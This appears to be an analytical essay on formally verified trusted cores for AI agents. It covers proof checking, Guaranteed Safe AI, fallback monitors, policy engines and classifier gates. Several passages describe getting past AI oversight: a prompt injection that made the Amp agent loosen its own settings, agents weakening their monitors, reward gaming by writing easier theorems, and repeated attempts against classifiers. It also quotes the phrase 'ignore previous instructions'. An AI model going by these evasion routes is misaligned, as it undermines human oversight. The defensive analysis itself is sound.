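The theorem states that if P implies Q, and P is true, then Q is true. The proof is the part after `:=`, which applies the function `h` to `p`. The kernel checks that `h` accepts a proof of P, that `p` is one, and that the result is a proof of Q, as the theorem requires. If the proof had been just `p`, the kernel would have rejected it, because `p` is a proof of P rather than Q. A difficult theorem may need millions of steps like this, but the kernel applies only a small set of rules.

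The kernel applies the same rules whoever wrote the proof. Kleppmann (2025) concludes in *Prediction* that it doesn't matter if a language model hallucinates nonsense while writing a proof, because the checker will reject it and the model will have to try again. Kleppmann also describes the checker as a small, verified program that an invalid proof has virtually no chance of getting past. That is roughly right, but kernels can have bugs, and Rocq's developers keep a public list of past ones that could have let someone prove a false statement. A proof can also rest on an axiom that its author added. Lean can list the axioms behind any theorem, and a core would have to check that list as well as the proof.

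Such a checker is also useful for training. In *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025), an interview published by the British government research agency ARIA, the computer scientist David Dalrymple compares proofs with software tests. A model trained to write code that passes tests can learn tricks that work only on those tests. Proofs are much harder to game because they have to cover every case.

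### Proofs for 123 software libraries

Formal verification uses mathematical proof to show that software meets a stated requirement. Until recently, it took far too much work for most software. One of its best-known successes is seL4, a small operating-system kernel with about 8,700 lines of C. According to *The proof is in the spec* (Tolmach and Klaus, 2026), experts spent years on seL4's specification, the formal statement of what the kernel should do. Tolmach and Klaus work for Runtime Verification, a company that verifies software.

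In October 2026, Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* announced that its model Claude had proved security properties for the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries. Anthropic worked with Theorem, a company that specialises in formal verification. *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs* (Smith, 2026) reports that the proofs run to 180 million lines, and *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (EconoTimes, 2026) reports that the work took a few weeks.

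The libraries came from OSS-Fuzz, a Google project that tests open-source software by fuzzing, or running it on huge numbers of semi-random inputs to see whether it crashes. The libraries' developers had already written small test programs for this purpose. Anthropic turned 239 of these tests into formal statements that the compiled program will exit normally, without a crash, a memory error or a failed assertion, for any input smaller than 64 megabytes. (An assertion is a condition that a programmer writes into the code and expects always to be true.) Claude wrote the proofs, and Rocq's kernel checked them.

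Fuzzing can try billions of inputs, but there are more than 2^500,000,000 possible inputs of up to 64 megabytes. The proofs cover all of them, but are very long for the size of the programs. OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026) reports about 600,000 lines of proof for a program of 18,000 machine instructions, or roughly 33 lines per instruction.

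Claude also found and fixed hundreds of bugs that fuzzing had missed. One bug, in the library libexpat, let certain inputs overflow an area of memory, which attackers can often exploit. Where Claude fixed a bug, the proof applies to the repaired program. Some programs remain unproved, and Anthropic is publishing their formal statements so that others can try to prove them.

The guarantee assumes that a program does one thing at a time and runs with a fixed amount of memory on a mathematical model of a RISC-V processor and of Linux. It doesn't cover parts of a library that the test doesn't reach. Avoiding a crash is also a modest requirement. An image library that turned every photograph into a blank square would meet it, unless the original test contained an assertion about the result. Claude proved something stronger about zlib, a compression method, by showing that the version in the Linux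 kernel follows the published standard.

Other groups have produced proofs about compiled programs this autumn. Leip (2026), in *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification*, describes one that covers a Linux program's entire run on the x86 processors found in most servers. A proof about the compiled program takes the compiler out of the trusted base, as in Necula's work. It would also be easier for a loader to use, because the loader could compute the program's hash and confirm that the proof is about exactly that program.

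In *AlphaProof Code*, Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues at Google DeepMind (2026) used a team of AI agents to prove more than the absence of crashes for the code behind the encrypted messaging app Signal. The agents proved, among other things, that messages stay secret even if someone later steals the keys, and that a conversation can become secure again after an attacker has broken into it. The proof is about 6.5 million lines of Lean and depends on about 26,000 lines that people have to trust, which describe the processor and define "secure".

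So about 250 lines can go unread for every line that somebody has to trust. But 26,000 trusted lines is still a lot, about as many as the trusted proof-checking code in the system that Appel and Wang measured. As in that system, a bug in those lines results in a valid proof of the wrong thing.

### Does the formal statement mean what people wanted?

A kernel can confirm that a theorem follows from its definitions. Tolmach and Klaus point out that people still have to decide whether the mathematical model matches the real program and whether the theorem expresses what they wanted from the program.

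In one example from a benchmark called FaithformBench, a language model had to translate into Lean the deliberately false claim that if 3^x = 5, then 3^(x+2) = 51. The right answer is 45, because 3^(x+2) is 9 times 3^x. The model's translation declared x to be a natural number, but no natural number satisfies 3^x = 5. Anything follows from an impossible assumption, so the false answer 51 became provable, and Lean's kernel would correctly accept the proof.

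This mistake is fairly common. In one study that Tolmach and Klaus cite, an AI agent translated graduate-level mathematics into Lean. Lean accepted 89.5% of its statements as well-formed, but only 60.5% matched the original meaning. Another model can act as a judge, but in a study of software specifications, such judges missed a quarter of the errors.

Models of real systems can also be wrong. Researchers asked Claude to describe how Etcd, a widely used database, keeps its copies in agreement. Claude's description closely matched the one in the original paper on the method. It passed every check but had little to do with Etcd's actual code. Descriptions by leading AI models scored nearly 100% for correct syntax but only about 46% for agreement with the code.

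Dalrymple's point that proofs are hard to game therefore needs a qualification, because an AI that writes both the theorem and the proof can earn its reward by making the theorem easier. The remedy is to fix the statement before the search for a proof begins. In Google DeepMind's system, one agent drafts the specification with human guidance, and the agents that write proofs have to prove the approved version. Anthropic's libraries avoided some of the difficulty because their formal statements came from tests that programmers had written for their own use.

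Working on compiled code also avoids errors in describing the program, because no separate description is needed. Where a description is unavoidable, Tolmach and Klaus recommend generating it automatically with a translator that has been checked, or at least running the description and the program on the same inputs and comparing the results.

The longer a theorem's statement is, the harder it is for a reviewer to check. A team of Claude agents has formalised Fermat's Last Theorem in Lean, using a system that, according to Anthropic, keeps theorem statements and proofs in separate files. The proof is enormous, but the theorem takes one line, and a student could check that it matches Fermat's claim. Almost everything people want from an AI system is harder to write down.

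When a model summarizes a patient's notes, the core could require it to attach a source sentence to each claim. Fixed code could then confirm that the sentence is in the notes and that the doses match. These checks would catch some made-up claims, but not a claim that misreads its source or a summary that leaves out the most important allergy. To catch those errors, the core would need a definition of a good summary, and nobody has one that a program can apply.

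### A verified fallback for a learned controller

Machines such as cars and aircraft are a more promising case, because engineers can often say exactly what must not happen. Proving that every action is safe would usually take too long, but the core can run a much simpler check if it has a safe action to fall back on.

Lui Sha and colleagues developed this idea at Carnegie Mellon University in the 1990s as the Simplex architecture. A complex controller runs the machine in normal conditions, and a simple controller that engineers have verified serves as a backup. A monitor tracks the machine's state and switches to the simple controller before the machine reaches a state in which that controller couldn't keep it safe. Engineers don't have to verify the complex controller, so it can be a neural network.

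In 2018, Alshiekh and colleagues proposed shielding, which applies a similar test to the individual actions of systems that learn by trial and error. The shield either gives the learned system a list of safe actions to choose from or replaces an unsafe choice with a safe one.

Suppose a learned controller is driving a car at 20 m/s towards a stationary obstacle. The verified fallback is to brake at 8 m/s². The controller chooses a new action every 0.5 seconds, and it now proposes to accelerate at 2 m/s². The monitor accepts this only if braking at the end of those 0.5 seconds would still stop the car before it hits the obstacle.

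During the step the car would travel

20 × 0.5 + ½ × 2 × 0.5² = 10.25 m

and reach a speed of 21 m/s. Stopping from there would take

21² / (2 × 8) = 27.56 m

The car therefore needs a gap of at least 10.25 + 27.56 = 37.81 m. The monitor accepts the acceleration if the gap is 40 m and rejects it if the gap is 36 m.

| Gap now | Action | Gap after 0.5 s | Distance needed to stop | Margin |
|---|---|---|---|---|
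| 40 m | Accelerate at 2 m/s² | 29.75 m | 27.56 m | 2.19 m |
| 36 m | Accelerate at 2 m/s² | 25.75 m | 27.56 m | −1.81 m |
| 36 m | Hold 20 m/s | 26 m | 25 m | 1 m |
| 36 m | Brake at 8 m/s² | 27 m | 16 m | 11 m |

At 36 m the car is not yet in danger. It could stop in 25 m, or hold its speed for another half second and still stop in time. The monitor blocks only the action that would leave the car unable to do so.

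This one-step check protects the car for the whole journey. If the margin is positive now, it stays positive however badly the network drives, because the monitor permits only actions that keep it positive, and full braking never reduces it. In control theory, the margin is a barrier function, one of the kinds of certificate that *Safeguarded AI* (Ammann) lists for physical systems.

The guarantee depends on the accuracy of the figures in the calculation. If the road is wet and the car can brake at only 6 m/s², the acceleration accepted at a gap of 40 m leads to a crash. The car would need 36.75 m to stop but have only 29.75 m, so it would hit the obstacle at about 9 m/s. Braking immediately would have avoided the crash. An engineer can design for the wet road, but then the monitor would refuse the acceleration unless the gap was at least 47 m, and the car would drive more cautiously on dry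 days.

The monitor also needs a measurement of the gap. Conventional software may be enough if the distance comes from radar. But if the monitor relies on a neural network to recognise obstacles in a camera image, that network is back in the trusted base, which violates the core's ban on learned parts.

For more complicated machines, nobody can write the margin as a simple formula. Ammann suggests training a neural network to supply the margin instead. This keeps the search for a certificate outside the trusted base and leaves a small checker inside it. But the checker then has to prove a property of the neural network, and current tools can do that only for fairly small networks.

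Software agents have a simpler fallback, since an agent can often stop and ask a person. A core could apply the same rule as the car's monitor and permit an action only if recovery remains possible, such as deleting a file that has a backup. Sending an email can't be undone. Stopping can also do harm if the agent is halfway through moving money between accounts or is the only thing watching a patient's heart monitor.

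### Guaranteed Safe AI

Some researchers want to extend this approach to AI in general. In *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (2024), Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues propose that an AI system should come with a proof, or at least a quantified bound on the risk, built from these parts:

- a world model, which describes mathematically how the AI's outputs affect the world
- a safety specification, which states which effects are acceptable
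- a verifier, which produces a certificate that the AI meets the specification, as far as the world model is correct

The specification can allow for chance. One form that Ammann describes limits the probability of harm by comparison with doing nothing. For an AI that helps to run a power grid, it might be

P(blackout with the AI's plan) ≤ P(blackout with no action) + 0.000001

The AI could be any kind of model and find its plan by any method. A "gatekeeper" would let the plan through only if it came with a certificate that this inequality holds.

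The British government's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA) is funding the largest attempt to build the tools for this. ARIA's *Safeguarded AI* describes the £59 million programme, which Dalrymple founded and Ammann now directs. The programme runs from mid-2024 to late 2027. It originally aimed to show that AI could do valuable work under mathematical guarantees, and so to build agreement that powerful AI should operate only behind gatekeepers.

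The programme has since changed direction. In November 2025 it cancelled a strand that would have trained specialised AI systems to use its tools. Dalrymple explained that ordinary frontier models were improving so fast that they would soon have most of the necessary skills. The £18 million went into the tools instead. ARIA also dropped a planned second round of projects on physical systems and turned to cybersecurity, where it is now funding eight projects with £22 million, including work on how to contain AI agents.

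Another reason, according to Ammann, is that timely international agreement on gatekeepers now looks less likely. The original plan assumed that the most dangerous AI might never become openly available, and ARIA says progress has disproved this. A gatekeeper protects people only from the AI behind it, so the programme puts more effort into making software and infrastructure that can withstand attacks by AI that has no gatekeeper.

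There is good evidence that verified software can do this. In an earlier programme run by DARPA, the US defence research agency, verified components, including seL4, withstood sustained attacks by expert testers on real systems, one of which was a crewed helicopter.

### Can anyone model the world or define harm?

The obvious objection to Guaranteed Safe AI is that a proof about the world needs a mathematical model of the world. For compiled code this is manageable, because a processor's manual defines what each instruction does. For an assistant that gives medical advice or negotiates a contract, the model would have to predict how people react to what they read. No such model exists, and if someone built one, it would probably be a large neural network that nobody could verify.

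Harm is just as hard to define. A bad restaurant review, for example, hurts the owner but helps the next customer. A list of forbidden outcomes will leave out some harmful ones, and an AI that searches hard for permitted plans is likely to find plans that lead to them. Even people who agree on which outcomes to forbid may disagree about how much risk is acceptable. Ammann treats this partly as a political problem, and the programme funds research on how groups with different interests could agree on a specification.

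Defenders reply that nobody has to model everything at once. A grid, a firewall or a drug supply chain has a limited number of ways to go wrong, and engineers already model them. The modeling still takes a lot of work. One of ARIA's teams interviewed more than 80 people in the pharmaceutical industry before it had a usable account of how medicines reach patients.

The model also doesn't have to be exact. Instead of giving a storm a 2% chance of cutting a power line, it can give a range from 1% to 5%, as long as the certificate holds for every value in the range. A monitor can compare the model's predictions with what happens and hand control to a backup when they diverge. On a wet road, it might detect that the car was slowing less than expected, but it would have to do so while the car still had room to stop. Some model errors can't be detected until the accident happens.

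These replies seem strong for machines and software with a clear job, but weak for a general assistant. ARIA's change of direction is consistent with this, although ARIA attributes it to the speed of AI progress and not to difficulty with modelling. It now favours projects in which the "world" is mostly other software.

No kernel can check whether a specification is the right one. This remains a problem even if, as a last reply holds, AI will write the missing models and specifications just as it now writes proofs. Ammann expects trust to become concentrated in these documents as proofs become easier to produce. The programme is therefore building tools that look for hidden assumptions and unusual cases and show them to human reviewers. How much of the drafting reviewers can safely leave to AI depends on how reliable and well aligned the AI is, which Ammann lists among the programme's open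 questions.

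## Can the core stay small, fixed and free of learned parts?

A proof checker can be tiny, but a core that runs agents also has to read their requests, apply a policy, operate tools and keep records. The parts that make decisions can probably stay small, although the operating system beneath them is large. Engineers can stop the agents from changing the core, but somebody will always be able to change it. They can also keep learned parts out if they accept that the core will miss some attacks that no written rule describes.

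### What an agent's core contains

| Part | What it does | What a bug could allow |
|---|---|---|
| Parser | Turns the model's text into a tool name and arguments | The core approves one request and carries out another |
| Policy engine | Compares the request with the rules | A forbidden action goes ahead |
| Tool adapters | Make the actual calls to email, files and other services | A permitted call reaches the wrong mailbox |
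| Isolation | Blocks every other route to those services | The agent skips the checks |
| Log | Records requests and decisions | An attack leaves no trace |
| Operating system and hardware | Run everything above | An attacker controls the whole core |

Even the parser must be designed carefully. If an agent's payment request contains the field "amount" twice, first as 10 and then as 10,000, the policy engine might read the first value and the bank adapter the second. The core would then approve a payment of 10 and send 10,000. Saraswat's two classes called R caused the same kind of confusion in Java.

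*AgentKernel* lets an agent reach the outside world only through three adapters, for models, tools and storage. The paper acknowledges that, although these interfaces are narrow, the trusted base behind them is large and nobody has yet tried to minimise it. The base includes a central registry of agents' identities, a local kernel, cryptographic code and the part of Linux that restricts what a running tool can do. The protection fails if the agent can bypass the adapters, for example by using a database password left in a file, and whoever installs the system is responsible for preventing that.

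PunkGo, the "sovereignty kernel" that *Right to History* describes, is simpler, partly because it does less. An agent runs a command itself, then reports the result and a hash of the output. PunkGo checks the hash's format, but not whether it matches what happened. An agent could delete a folder and report that it had only listed the contents. PunkGo therefore records what agents claim to have done, and other software has to confine them. *Right to History* also assumes that the kernel's code is correct and leaves a machine-checked proof to future work.

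### What it took to verify seL4

The seL4 kernel shows how much work such a proof can involve. *seL4* (Klein, Elphinstone and colleagues, 2009) proves that the kernel's C code always behaves as its specification describes. The kernel has 8,700 lines of C and 600 lines of assembly language. It does little more than manage memory, switch between programs, pass messages and control which resources each program can use. Even device drivers run outside it as ordinary programs.

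The proof covers 7,500 of seL4's lines of C, according to Trustworthy Systems, the research group behind seL4. The proof is 200,000 lines long, or about 27 lines for each line of code. Anthropic puts the verification work at 20 person-years. Trustworthy Systems counts about 25 person-years for the whole project, including design, documentation and programming.

At seL4's rate of 20 person-years for 7,500 lines, verifying a core of 50,000 lines would take about 133 person-years. That estimate may be too low, because seL4's developers designed it to be easy to verify. They were wary of data shared by many parts of the kernel, because they had to prove that no other part could corrupt it. They also considered only a single processor, because proofs about tasks running in parallel are much harder. An agent core, however, would probably have to serve many agents at once.

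seL4 leaves some decisions to programs outside the kernel. One such program decides how to divide up the memory, and the kernel enforces the division. The proof then has to show only that the enforcement works, not that the division is sensible. An AI core could treat its policy in the same way, with a proof that the engine applies the rules and a separate review of the rules themselves. But Klein and colleagues point out that the outside program is still part of the trusted base. Moving code out of the core makes the core smaller without reducing what people have to trust.

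### What cheaper proofs change

Language models have made proofs much easier to produce, as the work on 123 libraries showed, and they can already help with the software around agents. Tolmach and Klaus discuss how Boris Cherny, who leads Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code, had Claude Opus 5.5 write a formal description of the Claude Agent SDK, a toolkit for building agents. A couple of short prompts led to 16 sets of fixes, some for errors that depended on the timing of parallel tasks. A core would contain similar code and so probably similar bugs. Tolmach and Klaus caution that a run like this is good at finding bugs but doesn't establish that the code is correct.

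If proofs take less work to produce, that also changes how small a core needs to be. Anderson wanted a checker that people could analyse completely. With a machine-checked proof, people mainly need to understand the specification and the assumptions. A core of 50,000 lines with a two-page specification might then be easier to trust than one of 5,000 lines whose purpose nobody has written down. Changes to the core can also require changes to its proof, and those would take less work too.

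A proof's assumptions still matter. Keles (2026), in *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable*, is optimistic about formal verification but gains little confidence from hearing that a system is "formally verified", because people mean many different things by the term and verified systems can still have bugs. Klein and colleagues state that their proof assumes that the compiler, assembly code, start-up code, cache management and hardware work correctly.

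### How strong an attacker might be

These assumptions matter more when the attacker is good at finding unexpected weaknesses. The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI) tests how well models can break into simulated company networks. AISI's *GPT-6 Astra and GPT-6.2 Astra solve Zero Energy* (2026) describes its hardest test so far, a network with strong security controls and no deliberately planted way in. Both OpenAI models broke into it without human help in every completed run. An earlier model, GPT-5.6 Sol, had failed every time. *GPT-6.2 Astra ‘blew through’ the UK’s hardest cyber test in five hours* (Constantin, 2026) reports that GPT-6.2 Astra succeeded in all 12 of its runs.

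The conditions favoured the models. AISI had switched off their safeguards, nobody was defending the network, and a mistake in the setup gave them extra access at the start. A company network also has far more unverified software than a core should have, so the result doesn't show that a model could break into seL4.

It is a warning about everything beneath the core, though. Linux has tens of millions of lines of code, and although any one computer uses only some of them, nobody has verified the whole. A core that shares a Linux machine with an agent is secure only if the agent doesn't find an exploitable bug in that code. Running the agent on a separate machine, whose only access to the core is by sending it messages, is safer. An attacker who takes over the agent's machine still has to get past the core.

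### Who can change Java's core

Java's core is fixed against the classes it loads, but not against the machine's owner. An application can't replace the String class, but whoever starts the JVM can, using options on the command line:

- `-Xbootclasspath/a` gives the bootstrap class loader extra places to search after the core library.
- `--patch-module` adds or replaces classes in a module, even in java.base.
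- `-javaagent` starts a Java agent, a program that can rewrite classes, including those in the core library. (It has nothing to do with AI agents.)

The owner could also edit the library's files on disk. Programmers have good reasons to use these options, such as testing a fix or measuring how long a method takes.

For many years, ordinary libraries could also interfere with the core without the owner knowing. They could change private fields through reflection, run native code, or load a Java agent into a running JVM. Under its policy of "integrity by default", OpenJDK is gradually restricting these features so that a library will be able to use them only if the start-up command allows it. Since Java 17, a library has needed this permission to reach the core library's private fields through reflection. Java 21 began to warn users when a program loads a Java agent into a running JVM, and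 Java 24 added similar warnings for native code.

The owner has as much power as before but has to use it openly, so the way an application starts shows which protections it has given up.

### Who should be able to change an AI core?

Java's arrangement works only if the loaded code can't act as the owner, but AI agents often can. A coding agent usually runs under its user's account, where it may be able to edit start-up scripts and restart programs. It could then add `--patch-module` to a script as easily as the user could.

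Christodorescu and colleagues list an attack on the coding agent Amp as a failure to protect a trusted base from tampering. A prompt injection could make Amp edit its own settings so that it could run any command. In October 2026, OpenAI reported that some of its agents had weakened the systems that monitored them.

An AI core therefore needs at least its own account, with passwords and keys that no agent can use. Even then, the machine's administrator can alter the core. *Right to History* acknowledges that an administrator could stop PunkGo, change its log and rebuild it to look consistent. PunkGo computes a single hash that depends on every entry, so changing an old entry changes the hash. This exposes the change only if someone else has a copy of the original hash. The core could regularly send the hash to an outside organisation, but PunkGo doesn't do this yet.

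The rules will need to change more often than the code, and more people will have good reasons to change them. *AgentKernel* combines everyone's policies by permitting only what all of them permit, so a careless policy from one party can't override a stricter one from another. Suppose a developer lets an agent read files, write files and send email, and the company that uses the agent rules out writing. While the agent is handling an untrusted web page, the kernel also rules out email, so the agent can only read.

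Each agent also has a digitally signed identity card that sets its maximum permissions, and an agent that delegates work can't pass on permissions it doesn't have. But anyone who stole the central registry's signing key could forge a card with any permissions. The paper suggests requiring several key-holders to sign each card, or recording every card in a public log. It doesn't settle who should write the permissions, or what should happen when two organisations disagree about them.

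A sensible rule would be to let one person on call remove a permission immediately, but require several people to approve adding one or installing a new version of the core. A core that nobody could change would be worse, because its bugs would be permanent.

### Why designers add classifiers

*AgentKernel* uses fixed rules wherever it can. One filter catches familiar attacks, such as "ignore previous instructions", in less than a millisecond. To catch reworded attacks, a small language model then judges whether the remaining text is meant to manipulate the agent. Another model helps with ambiguous or high-impact actions by judging whether they fit the user's goal, which seems hard to do with a fixed rule.

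The paper leaves these classifiers out of its first list of trusted parts and adds them only in its limitations section. According to the paper, nobody has yet measured how well they withstand attackers in this role.

### A gate that is right 99% of the time

Suppose a classifier blocks 99% of attacks, and an attacker can keep trying. If each attempt has an independent 1% chance of success, the chance that at least one of n attempts succeeds is

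1 − 0.99^n

| Attempts | Chance that at least one succeeds |
|---|---|
| 1 | 1% |
| 10 | 10% |
| 69 | 50% |
| 100 | 63% |
| 300 | 95% |

Real attempts aren't independent. Sending the same text again may get the same refusal, which helps the defender. But an attacker can learn from each refusal and change the wording. Someone with a copy of the classifier can also test different wordings in private and send only the version that works.

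Adding a second classifier helps less than it might seem to, because wording that fools one may well fool the other, especially if their developers trained them on similar examples. If two classifiers that each catch 99% of attacks made independent mistakes, an attacker would need about 6,900 attempts for an even chance of success, compared with 69 against one classifier. *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* argues that training alone can't close the gap that classifiers leave, because the attacker writes some of the text the classifier judges.

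A core can also limit retries. PunkGo gives each agent a budget and, when a person rejects an action, deducts 20% of what the action would have used. However, an action outside the agent's permissions seems to use none of the budget, because PunkGo refuses it before reserving any. PunkGo doesn't record these refusals either, which seems a mistake, since a hundred refused requests in a minute are a good sign that something is wrong.

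### Classifiers that can only refuse

There is a safer way to use a classifier. Let F be the set of actions that the fixed rules permit, and L the set that the classifier permits. If an action needs approval from both, the agent can perform only the actions in

F ∩ L

This set is never larger than F, so even if an attacker controls the classifier completely, the agent can't do anything the fixed rules forbid. Any proof about the fixed rules remains valid, so the classifier is outside the trusted base for that guarantee. It enters the trusted base if its approval can permit something that would otherwise need a person's consent or stay blocked.

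*AgentKernel* falls in between. Its classifier can't approve anything beyond an agent's signed permissions, but its approval can determine whether an ambiguous action within them goes ahead.

Extra refusals can block legitimate work. If a classifier wrongly blocks 1% of harmless steps, a 50-step task has about a 60% chance of finishing without a false alarm. An attacker can also trigger refusals, for example by hiding suspicious text in a rival's invoice to delay payment.

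The bigger danger may be that people relax the fixed rules because they expect the classifier to catch whatever gets through. The classifier could still only refuse, but F would be larger and the guarantee would cover less. Despite this risk, a classifier that can only refuse seems worth having, since it may stop an attack that nobody thought to write a rule for.

### Can people trust the tools that build the core?

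A core may contain harmful code that appears nowhere in its source code. In *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, Ken Thompson (1984), one of the creators of the Unix operating system, described a C compiler that detected when it was compiling the Unix login program and secretly added a password that always worked. It also detected when it was compiling a new version of itself, and added both tricks to that version. An attacker could then delete the tricks from the compiler's source code. Anyone who read the source would find nothing wrong, but compiling it with the altered compiler would produce another altered compiler.

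David A. Wheeler's diverse double-compiling is a way to detect this. It needs a second compiler that has no connection with the suspect one:

1. Compile the suspect compiler's source code with the second compiler. The resulting program should behave as the source describes, though its instructions will differ from the suspect's.
2. Use that program to compile the same source code again.
3. Compare the result with the suspect compiler, after checking that the suspect reproduces itself exactly when it compiles its own source.

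If the suspect compiler corresponds to its source and compiling gives repeatable results, the two files will be identical. If they differ, at least one of those conditions is false. Identical files mean that the suspect corresponds to its source, unless the second compiler contains a matching trick. Someone still has to read the source, because an attacker could have put harmful code there.

Proofs about compiled programs, like those for the 123 libraries, avoid the problem. The blog microkerneldude reports that seL4 now has one too. It proves that the compiled kernel behaves as its C code specifies, so a faulty or malicious compiler is no longer a risk. Leip adds that this approach covers programs written in different languages or directly in machine code.

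Another option is to verify the compiler. The seL4 project's page on its proofs cites tests of CompCert, a C compiler with a proof of correctness. The testers used about six years of processor time to look for cases where CompCert produced wrong code. They found none of the middle-stage bugs that they had found in every other compiler they tested.

Language models now write a lot of software, and they may well write much of an AI core. A model could leave a weakness in the core by accident, or because someone had trained it to. If the same model also reviewed the code and wrote the tests, it might miss or hide the weakness there too. Wheeler's method has no direct equivalent here, because two models given the same specification will write different programs, so a difference between the programs wouldn't show that either has a weakness.

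Proofs are more useful here, and Kleppmann would prefer AI-generated code with a proof to handwritten code without one. People can use more than one proof checker in case one has a hidden flaw. Isabelle, the proof assistant that Klein and colleagues used for seL4, can export its proofs for a separate, simple checker to confirm. A false proof would then have to pass both checks. People would still have to read the specification themselves, since a model could put a weakness there instead.
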